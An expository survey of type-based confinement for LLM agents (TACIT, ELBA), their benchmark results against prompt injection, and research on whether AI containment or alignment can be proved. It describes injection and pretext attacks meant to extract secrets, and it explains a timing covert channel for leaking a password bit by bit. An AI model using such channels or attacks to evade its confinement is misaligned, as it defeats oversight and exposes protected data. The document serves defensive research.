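Odersky and colleagues' system, TACIT, checks each piece of an agent's code before running it. The agent writes short programs in Scala 3, a typed language. It can reach files, commands and the network only through TACIT's library, which hands out capabilities as ordinary program values. Scala's types can record which capabilities a function uses:

| Type | Functions it describes |
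|---|---|
| `String -> Int` | Those that use no capabilities, called pure |
| `String ->{f} Int` | Those that may use the capability `f` |
| `String => Int` | Those that may use any capability |

A pure function can compute a result but cannot print, write to a file or contact another machine. TACIT relies on this to protect secrets. When the agent reads a file from a folder marked as classified, it receives a `Classified[String]` instead of a `String`. This is an abstract type, so the agent's code cannot take the text out. It can only pass a function to the type's `map` operation:

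```scala
def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`map` applies the function to the hidden value and hides the result again. Because of the arrow `->`, the function must be pure.

Here is a program that TACIT accepts, adapted from one of its authors' examples:

```scala
val summary = requestFileSystem("/data") {
  val letter = readClassified("secret/salaries.txt")
  chat("Summarize this letter", letter)
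}
println(summary)
```

1. `requestFileSystem` gives the code between the braces access to files under `/data`.
2. `readClassified` returns the letter as a `Classified[String]`.
3. `chat` sends the letter to a separate, trusted model and returns its summary, which is also a `Classified[String]`.
4. The block returns the summary. Its type mentions no file capability, so it may leave the block.
5. `println` shows the summary to the user, but the agent's model sees only `Classified(****)`.

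The agent can continue working with the summary in later turns. For example, `summary.map(_.length)` computes its length, which also remains hidden from the agent.

Now suppose the agent tries to print the letter from inside `map`:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/data") {
  val letter = readClassified("secret/salaries.txt")
  letter.map { text => println(text) }
}
```

Printing requires a capability, here called `io`. The compiler infers that the function has type `String ->{io} Unit`, where `Unit` means that it returns nothing useful. `map` requires a function of type `String -> Unit`, so the types do not match and the compiler rejects the program. TACIT runs none of it, so the program never opens the letter. For the same reason, the compiler rejects programs that send the text over the network or write it to a file. The same check raises a false alarm on the harmless `letter.map { text =>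 println("done") }`.

This design also blocks the kind of implicit leak described earlier. The agent can test whether the letter contains a certain number, but the result is a `Classified[Boolean]`, and `if` accepts only an ordinary `Boolean`. A function passed to `map` can branch on the letter, but it can only produce another hidden value.

Types also limit how long a permission lasts. If a program returns a function that would read a file after the permission ends, the function's type must refer to the file capability. That capability has no meaning outside the braces, so the compiler rejects this program too.

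TACIT compiles the agent's code in a "safe mode" that forbids language features that can bypass its checks, such as unchecked casts. Library authors can still use these features in modules that they mark as safe, much as Rust's library authors use unsafe code. Some checks happen only at run time. For example, TACIT stops a program if it tries to access a file outside `/data`. Proofs exist for the basic system that tracks capabilities, but Odersky and colleagues have not yet proved that safe mode as a whole provides its intended guarantees.

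### How TACIT performed

Odersky and colleagues tested for leaks by giving agents a software project with a folder of secrets. They combined each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 injection attacks, for 120 trials. In another 11 trials, a malicious user asked for secrets directly or under a pretext, such as an emergency password change. Two models each went through all 131 trials twice, once with classified types and once with ordinary strings. The table shows the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output.

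| Model | Trials | Classified types | Ordinary strings |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with injections | 100% | 100% |
| | 11 with a malicious user | 100% | 81.8% |
| | All 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| | 11 with a malicious user | 100% | 27.3% |
| | All 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

Without the types, Claude leaked secrets in two trials and MiniMax in 11. Ten of those 13 leaks came from the malicious set, which has only 11 tasks, so one task changes the score on that set by 9 percentage points. The totals also depend on the mix of trials, and if the two sets had equal weight, MiniMax would score about 62 per cent without the types instead of 91.6.

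131 trials without a leak would not alone rule out a true leak rate of about 2 per cent. The stronger evidence for TACIT is the rule that the compiler applies to every program, and the tests mainly check that the implementation follows that rule.

The agents could still do ordinary tasks with the types in place. On the 120 trials with such tasks, Claude answered correctly in 99.2 per cent with classified types and 83.3 per cent without. MiniMax answered correctly in 90.0 per cent with them and 88.3 per cent without. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Claude's low score without the types is partly an artefact, because Claude often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

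They also compared typed programs with ordinary tool calls on two established benchmarks. On τ²-bench, in which agents handle customer service for an airline and a shop, three models each scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with typed programs. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 programming problems, MiniMax solved 41.7 per cent with TACIT and 43.3 per cent without it, a difference of five problems.

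The models were probably trained on little code that uses this experimental part of Scala. Even so, only 0.32 to 7.93 per cent of their programs on τ²-bench needed another attempt, depending on the model and task, and those programs needed fewer than 1.4 retries on average.

TACIT also blocked all but one of 1,926 attacks in AgentDojo. In the exception, the agent booked the hotel the user wanted but quoted a review that recommended another, and the benchmark counted the mention of the other hotel as a success for the attacker. Odersky and colleagues say that TACIT and CaMeL completed comparable numbers of tasks, but the results vary widely. With OpenAI's o4-mini, TACIT completed 52.9 per cent of the office tasks and CaMeL 81.4 per cent. With Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64.3 per cent of the travel tasks and CaMeL 1.4 per cent.

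### ELBA: effect types in Haskell

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) uses Haskell, a language in which a program's type shows what effects it may have. A program of type `Int` can only compute a whole number. If a user asks a calculator agent to delete all the files on a server before computing a factorial, the model may write code to do that. But deleting files is an input/output effect, so the code has a type beginning with `IO` instead of the type `Int`, and the compiler rejects it.

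A developer can define a narrower effect type for each task. Zhou and colleagues' system, ELBA, includes an agent that compiles bibliographies and may write only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. In simplified form, the relevant functions are:

```haskell
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
writeFile       :: FilePath -> String -> IO ()
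```

The agent's program must have type `BibIO ()`, so it cannot call `writeFile`, whose type is `IO ()`. It also cannot invent an entry, because only `dblpFetchBib` produces a `Trusted Bib`. The agent can still sort and filter entries freely. In a test with 100 topics, an ordinary agent got the authors, year or DOI (a paper's identifier) wrong in 19 of 1,002 citations. ELBA's agent made no such mistakes in 925 citations.

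An agent's program can call another agent, for example to decide what to do after reading a search result. The second agent's program must fit the type the first one expects, so it is subject to the same policy or a stricter one. Zhou and colleagues proved that adding such calls does not weaken any guarantee the language's types already give. Their proof replaces each call with an ordinary function that gets a program from the model, checks its type and runs it. The result is an ordinary program in the original language, so the existing guarantee still applies.

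For information flow, ELBA relies on an older Haskell library, LIO. The type checker ensures that the agent's program can act only through LIO, but LIO tracks and checks labels while the program runs, so a program that passes the type check may still stop partway with an error.

### What ELBA's policy adds

Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL on AgentDojo's Slack tasks, which involve a workplace messaging service. They used four models from Anthropic and OpenAI. Without attacks, each model completed this many of the 21 tasks:

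| | ELBA | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| With the policy | 8 to 10 | 4 to 6 |
| Without the policy | 14 to 18 | 13 to 17 |

With its policy on, ELBA completed almost twice as many tasks as CaMeL, but both systems failed many tasks that they could complete with their policies off. ELBA also took about three times as long, mainly because its agents call the model again after reading new data.

The benchmark pairs each of the 21 tasks with five attacks, making 105 combinations. Every model resisted all 105 in both systems, even without a policy, so the test cannot show how much protection either policy adds.

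Zhou and colleagues then removed the models' own resistance. When an agent's input contained a planted instruction, they replaced its whole prompt with that input, so that it received the attacker's instructions as its task. They ran the 105 combinations seven times for each model, which gives 735 runs:

| Model | Attacks resisted, no policy | Attacks resisted, with policy | Tasks completed, no policy | Tasks completed, with policy |
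|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 425 | 735 | 523 | 351 |
| Opus 4.8 | 460 | 735 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT 5.4 | 621 | 735 | 558 | 338 |
| Sonnet 5 | 540 | 735 | 494 | 294 |

The policy stopped every attack. Without it, up to 42 per cent would have succeeded. The benchmark counted 29 of the runs as successful attacks because the agent had opened a certain web page, but Zhou and colleagues reviewed them by hand and found no violation of the policy. The policy also reduced the number of completed tasks by about 33 to 44 per cent, depending on the model. This is a better test of the policy than the original benchmark because the result does not depend on whether a model recognises an attack.

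### Limits of these checks

A program that passes the check can still give wrong answers, as with other type systems, and TACIT does not try to prevent a model's factual or logical mistakes. ELBA's bibliography agent can write a genuine entry for an irrelevant paper. A sentence planted in a contract can distort the summary TACIT shows the user, though it cannot make the agent send the contract to anyone.

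Odersky and colleagues also leave covert channels such as timing out of scope. A pure function could run for a long time if the first bit of a password is 1 and finish quickly if it is 0. The agent could learn that bit by measuring how long its program took, then learn the next bit the same way.

TACIT's guarantee also does not cover external commands, which the Scala compiler does not check. Odersky and colleagues therefore recommend allowing only specific safe commands and adding a sandbox where security is critical.

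All these systems also depend on people writing labels and interfaces correctly. TACIT classifies files by folder, so if somebody saves a copy of the salary letter in an ordinary folder, the agent can read and send it. If a developer declares that a function for reading mail returns a `String` instead of a `Classified[String]`, the compiler will accept programs that leak the mail. Girrens and Wang make a similar point about CaMeL, whose guarantee depends on a separate policy for each tool.

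Such code is moderate in size. TACIT's shared library has about 1,000 lines, and the airline and shop interfaces have a few hundred each. Odersky and colleagues suggest that agents could draft new interfaces from existing tool descriptions, and people could review them before use. The reviewers would then read each interface once instead of reading every program the agent writes.

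## Test claims that a whole AI system can or cannot be proved safe

TACIT and ELBA guarantee only narrow properties of the programs that a model writes. Some researchers argue that nobody can ever prove that a whole AI system, including the model, is safe. Others argue that builders should prove this before they run the system. To judge either claim, one needs to know which programs and inputs it covers and how it defines "safe".

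### Deciding whether a program harms humans

Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues (2021), in *Superintelligence Cannot be Contained*, argue that nobody can fully contain a superintelligence, a machine far more intelligent than any human. Their proof reuses the construction from the file property, with harm in place of the forbidden read. A program runs an arbitrary harmless computation and then calls `harm_humans()`, so it harms people exactly when the computation halts. An exact test for harm would therefore solve the halting problem.

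The proof is correct, but it covers all programs and all inputs. Alfonseca and colleagues reach a conclusion about a superintelligence by also assuming that its program can simulate every other program, that its input can contain any program, and that its language includes an operation that harms humans.

A machine's actions can be predictable even if it can simulate every program. For example, suppose an interpreter can run any computation but can act only by displaying a number. No procedure can always tell whether it will stop, but it clearly will never send an e-mail. McCann's boundary relies on the same separation between computing and acting. The impossibility argument requires a machine that also performs the harmful operation whenever the simulated program stops, with no gate to block it.

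The definition of containment is also strict. A control must block the machine when there is reason to predict harm and allow it otherwise, so it can never raise a false alarm. Alfonseca and colleagues conclude that any practical method will have some error rate, however small. But those errors could all be false alarms, as they are for any sound checker. The theorem does not show how much useful work such a checker would have to block.

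### One program or all programs

*Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021), from CSER, a Cambridge research centre on existential risk, objects that such an argument would rule out proofs about any program, as did the forum reply about Rice's theorem described earlier. Yet researchers have proved that an entire operating system meets its specification. *On Controllability of AI* (2020) had already noted that the result of Alfonseca and colleagues holds only for arbitrary programs. CSER adds that engineers could build an AI that does not run arbitrary subroutines.

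The objection is logically right, but a proof about one particular system may still be too hard to produce. CSER itself warns that AI programs may be too complex to predict in practice. Even tiny programs can be hard to predict. In 1989, Heiner Marxen and Jürgen Buntrock found a Turing machine with five states that stops after 47,176,870 steps. Nobody proved until 2024 that this is the most steps any five-state machine of the same kind can take before stopping. An AI system is far larger, and a proof about one that takes requests from the public must cover every request that anyone might send.

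The preprint version, *Superintelligence cannot be contained* (2016), concedes that people use billions of programs without formal guarantees and are confident, for practical purposes, that a phone will not start a nuclear war. Alfonseca and colleagues doubt that this confidence carries over to a superintelligence. Their doubt is reasonable, but it comes from a lack of experience with such machines, not from the theorem.

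### Certificates for neural networks

An AI system is "aligned" if it behaves as people intend. In *No Certificate for Alignment*, Agarwal (2026) considers a verifier that reads a description of an AI system and decides whether it is aligned. Ideally, the verifier would be sound, complete and fast, where "fast" means that its running time grows at most polynomially with the size of the system. Agarwal argues that a verifier can have any two of these properties but not all three. The result applies to verifiers that must be right about every system in a broad class, on all inputs, and it assumes that alignment has been defined mathematically.

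Agarwal supports the claim that a sound and complete verifier cannot always be fast with earlier results about neural networks built from ReLU units, which output their input if it is positive and 0 otherwise. Checking even simple numerical properties of such networks is NP-complete, so nobody knows a method that is fast in every case, and most computer scientists believe that none exists. For systems that can carry out any computation, Rice's theorem shows that no algorithm can decide nontrivial properties of their behaviour in every case. Agarwal notes that the theorem does not cover current language models, because they read a limited amount of text at a time and calculate with limited precision. The obstacle to verifying a single model is therefore running time, not undecidability.

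These are worst-case results. In *AI Alignment Is Neither Solvable nor Sufficient*, Großmann (2026) argues that nobody can guarantee alignment in open-ended use, but accepts that such results do not make every restricted system hard to verify.

The claim that a sound and fast verifier must reject some aligned systems rests on a different argument. Suppose a system contains one number θ. For inputs between 0 and 1, it returns 1 if the input is greater than θ and 0 otherwise, and it counts as aligned if θ is at most 0.05. A verifier tries the inputs 0.1, 0.2, ..., 0.9. Systems with θ = 0.04 and θ = 0.06 both return 1 every time, so the verifier can't distinguish them. To be sound, it must reject the system with θ = 0.06, so it must also reject the aligned one.

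Agarwal's argument is a good one about verifiers that can only try inputs, but it does not apply in the same way to verifiers that read the system's text. Such a verifier can look up θ and compare it with 0.05. The earlier proof about the summing loop also covered every `n` without running the program.

Agarwal's own experiment used interval bound propagation, which calculates with ranges of numbers instead of trying individual inputs. If x and y both lie between 0.5 and 1, then 2x − y lies between 0 and 1.5. The ranges it finds always contain the true values but can be too wide. For example, it calculates that x − x, which is always 0, lies between −0.5 and 0.5, because it treats the two x's as if they could differ.

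Agarwal trained a small network with two inputs to return at least 0.5 whenever both inputs lie between 0.5 and 1. The largest box of inputs that the method certified covered 49 per cent of this region. That box contains infinitely many inputs, so a finite calculation can certify infinitely many cases. For the whole region, the method could guarantee only an output of at least 0.0002. Agarwal presents this failure as an example of the theorem, but the ranges may just have been too wide. The rejection may even have been correct, since the network was right on only 95 per cent of a grid of test points.

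### Systems that rewrite themselves

A certificate for today's system may not apply after the system changes its own program. Gumbau Mezquita (2026), in *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic*, models self-modification as a fixed rule that turns every program into its next version. The theorem states that no procedure can decide, for every program, whether the next version has the same safety status as the current one. It assumes the following:

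- Safety depends only on the function that a program computes.
- Programs that compute the same function have next versions that compute the same function.
- The rule makes at least one safe program unsafe.
- A program that never returns counts as unsafe, and so does its next version.

Under these assumptions, "keeps its safety status" is a non-trivial extensional property, so Rice's theorem applies to it. The second assumption fits real systems poorly, because a system that edits its own text may treat two programs differently when their text differs, even if they compute the same function.

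Gumbau Mezquita also concludes that only a system whose behaviour has stopped changing can have a lasting certificate. That does not follow, as this rule shows:

```python
def next_version(f):
    def g(n):
        if f(0) == f(1):
            return f(n) + 2
        return 1
    return g
```

In this example, a program is safe if it returns an even number for every input. This rule meets all four assumptions. For instance, a program that returns 0 for the input 0 and 2 for every other input is safe, but its next version always returns 1. Another program always returns 0, and its later versions always return 2, then 4, then 6, and so on. Its behaviour changes at every step, but every version is safe because adding 2 to an even number gives an even number. The theorem rules out a procedure that works for all starting programs, but it doesn't rule out a proof about this one.

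Gumbau Mezquita accepts that the theorem need not apply if a system can change itself only in a few fixed ways, though this limits how much it can improve. A system could also stop after each change and wait for a new check. Gumbau Mezquita argues that having one AI supervise another doesn't help, because a supervisor that can understand a general system must itself be general and will change too. But a supervisor that only checks proofs can be a small program that never changes. As with proof-carrying code, the system would have to supply a proof with each new version, and could not adopt a version without one, even if that version was safe.

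### Build the system from proven parts

Melo, Máximo and colleagues (2024), in *On the Undecidability of Artificial Intelligence Alignment*, accept that no procedure can decide whether an arbitrary AI system is aligned. They propose building only systems whose construction guarantees alignment. The builder starts with a finite set of parts proved to be aligned and a finite set of operations proved to preserve alignment. Every system built from them is then aligned, and there are infinitely many such systems. Typing rules work the same way, since the type of an expression follows from the types of its parts.

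Whether a property of the parts carries over to the whole system depends on the property. If two parts always stop, a system that runs one after the other also always stops, but a system that runs them in a loop may not. Secrecy is harder to preserve because, as with the letter about salaries, two parts that are each harmless alone can leak a secret together. Großmann similarly argues that a group of agents can cause harm even if each agent is aligned.

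Melo and colleagues also describe a way to add the property to any model that always stops. A judge function checks whether each output is acceptable for its input. If it isn't, the system instead returns a fixed output that the judge accepts. For a model that should return a probability, the judge could require a number between 0 and 1. Melo and colleagues say the main practical difficulty is defining the judge.

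The paper requires the model to stop because otherwise the judge may never receive an output. A language model meets this requirement if its software limits the length of each reply. An agent that calls the model in a loop may run forever, so the paper proposes a counter or another mechanism that forces the agent into a final state.

They claim that if a system always stops, other properties, including alignment, become decidable. This is true only if the size of the input is also limited, because a checker could then try every input, though usually not in any practical time. For example, the function `q` from the discussion of total languages always stops, but no exact check of its file property over all inputs exists. A gate that checks each action works even if the agent never stops, because it can refuse a forbidden action whenever one arrives.

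The 2025 journal version has a bolder title, *Machines that halt resolve the undecidability of artificial intelligence alignment*. Gumbau Mezquita replies that checking a single fixed, finite system is decidable, though possibly intractable, but that no procedure can decide whether a property holds on every possible finite hardware configuration. Both claims are true, but a builder who needs a guarantee for one known machine needs only the first kind of check.

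### Guaranteed Safe AI

Dalrymple and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, propose proving things about what a system does in the physical world. Their framework has three components:

- The specification states which outcomes are acceptable.
- The world model predicts how the system's actions affect its surroundings.
- The verifier produces a proof that, if the world model is right, the system meets the specification, or that the risk of a violation stays below a stated limit.

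Suppose a delivery drone must stay at least 5 metres from people. The world model allows for an error of up to 1 metre in the drone's measured distance and for wind that pushes it up to 2 metres off course. The verifier proves that the drone's software always plans a route at least 8 metres from anybody. Since 8 − 1 − 2 = 5, the drone meets the specification in the model. If a gust pushes the real drone 4 metres off course, it may come within 3 metres of somebody even though the proof contains no mistake, because the model underestimated the wind.

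Max Tegmark and Steve Omohundro (2023) go further, calling such proofs "the only path to controllable AGI" in the subtitle of *Provably Safe Systems*. (AGI, or artificial general intelligence, means AI that can do most of what people can.) They expect AI to do much of the work of finding the proofs, which simple programs can then check.

In the talk *Provably Safe AI*, Tegmark describes a neural network that had learned to add numbers. An automated tool worked out the network's algorithm and wrote it as a Python program. The researchers then used Dafny to prove that the program adds all numbers correctly, including those outside the training data. Tegmark calls this a toy example. Addition has a short specification that nobody disputes. The proof applies to the extracted program, so anyone who wants the guarantee has to run that program or prove separately that the network computes the same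 function.

### Missing models and missing data

In *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, Dickson (2024) objects that proofs apply to systems of symbols and not to the physical world. For example, engineers used a verification tool to rule out certain software errors in the lander that took the Perseverance rover to Mars in 2021, but the tool guaranteed nothing about the weather, the hardware or the landing itself. Dickson reports that about half of all Mars missions have failed and attributes about 20 per cent of the risk to software. If those figures are right, removing every software failure would lower the failure rate only from about 50 to about 40 per cent.

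Many of the risks that worry AI researchers are harder to model than a landing. Dickson argues that proving a new virus harmless would require simulating its effects on a human body for years. In 2022, researchers simulated 20 minutes in the life of one very simple cell, and a human body has about 36 trillion cells. Even a perfect model would need data about the particular body. Google's map of about a millionth of a human brain takes up 1.4 petabytes, so a map of a whole brain at the same detail would need about a million times as much. The talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* adds that much of human biology is still unknown. It also says that formally verified software is worth having but does not replace other work on AI safety.

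Proponents answer that Dickson has chosen needlessly hard properties. They do not claim that every desirable property can be proved by some method. Their examples include a DNA synthesiser that cannot make certain pathogens, a computer that nobody can log in to without the right credentials, and AI hardware that works only in a certain place or for a limited time. A synthesiser can refuse known pathogens by comparing each requested sequence with a list, without simulating a human body. Dickson also says the proponents want failure rates of 0 per cent, but the DNA proposal he criticises requires only that the risk be below a conservative limit.

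The answer works for the narrower properties because they leave out most of what made the original question hard. Whether a DNA sequence matches anything on a list is a syntactic property, but a sequence that is not on the list may still be dangerous. The 2026 proofs about LLMbda and ELBA cover labels and types, not whether an agent's actions help or harm anybody.

Gödel's completeness theorem guarantees a proof only for statements that are true in every structure that satisfies the axioms. One proponent also cites the theorem to argue that every safety property that really holds has a formal proof, but that does not follow. Any fixed set of sound proof rules leaves some good programs without a proof, as the discussion of proof-carrying code showed. To prove a claim about drones or viruses, somebody must also first write axioms that describe them correctly, which Dickson considers out of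 reach.

### From memory errors to harm

A soundness proof for a type system connects two mathematical objects, the typing rules and the rules for running programs, so designers of type systems never had to model people or the weather. In the small language from the section on typing rules, a program goes wrong if it gets stuck, and the language's own rules define what that means. Rust's designers likewise decide which operations count as undefined behaviour. The hardware still has to follow the rules for running programs, but engineers build processors to do that. A proof that an AI system causes no harm has to connect the system's outputs to events in the world, and those events to what people mean by harm.

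Three specifications for an office agent show how the task grows:

| Specification | What somebody must define | What the proof needs a model of |
|---|---|---|
| No write outside a folder | Which operations are writes, which files are inside, and whose writes count | The file system and the operating system's calls |
| No customer data sent out | Which data belongs to customers, who counts as an outsider, and which disclosures are allowed | Every program and service that handles the data |
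| No harm | Who counts, what harms them, compared with what alternative, and over how long | People, institutions and the physical world |

The folder rule requires the target of each write to be in the permitted set of files. The builder still has to decide how the rule applies in some cases. Deleting or renaming a file should probably count as a write. On many systems one file can have two names, so a file inside the folder may also have a name outside it. The agent might also ask another program to write for it. But the operating system's documentation describes these cases, and a sandbox can enforce the rule on each write without predicting what the agent will do.

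Requiring each message to meet a condition is not enough to protect customer data, because a message may summarise or encode the data. Noninterference is a precise starting point, but it is too strict for most companies, since it forbids sending a customer his own invoice or announcing the number of customers. The company therefore has to list the disclosures it allows and label the data correctly wherever it is stored, so that a type system like TACIT's can enforce the policy. If the company trained its model on customers' letters, the model may repeat parts of them even when the agent has opened no labelled file.

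The word "harm" has no comparable starting point. Suppose an agent schedules a hospital's appointments. Moving one patient forward moves another back, so almost any schedule makes someone wait longer than they would under another. Whether the delay counts as harm depends on the patients' conditions, what would otherwise have happened, and how one weighs different people's interests.

Großmann distinguishes three difficulties: choosing whose values should guide the system, finding out what people want and what an action will cause, and keeping up as values change. AI systems may cause some of that change. In one of Großmann's examples, an AI helps a drug company improve how a protein binds to its target. The work seems harmless, but if a pathogen that relies on a similar interaction appears later, the same knowledge could help somebody cause harm. Inspecting the program would not reveal this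 risk, because the risk depends on a fact outside the program.

A system that satisfies the first two specifications can still cause harm. The hospital's agent could write the wrong dose in a patient's record while staying inside the permitted folder and sending nothing out. The hospital can catch some of these errors with another narrow rule, such as that no dose may exceed the published maximum for the patient's weight. A checker can apply this rule easily, but a dose below the maximum may still be dangerous for a patient with weak kidneys.
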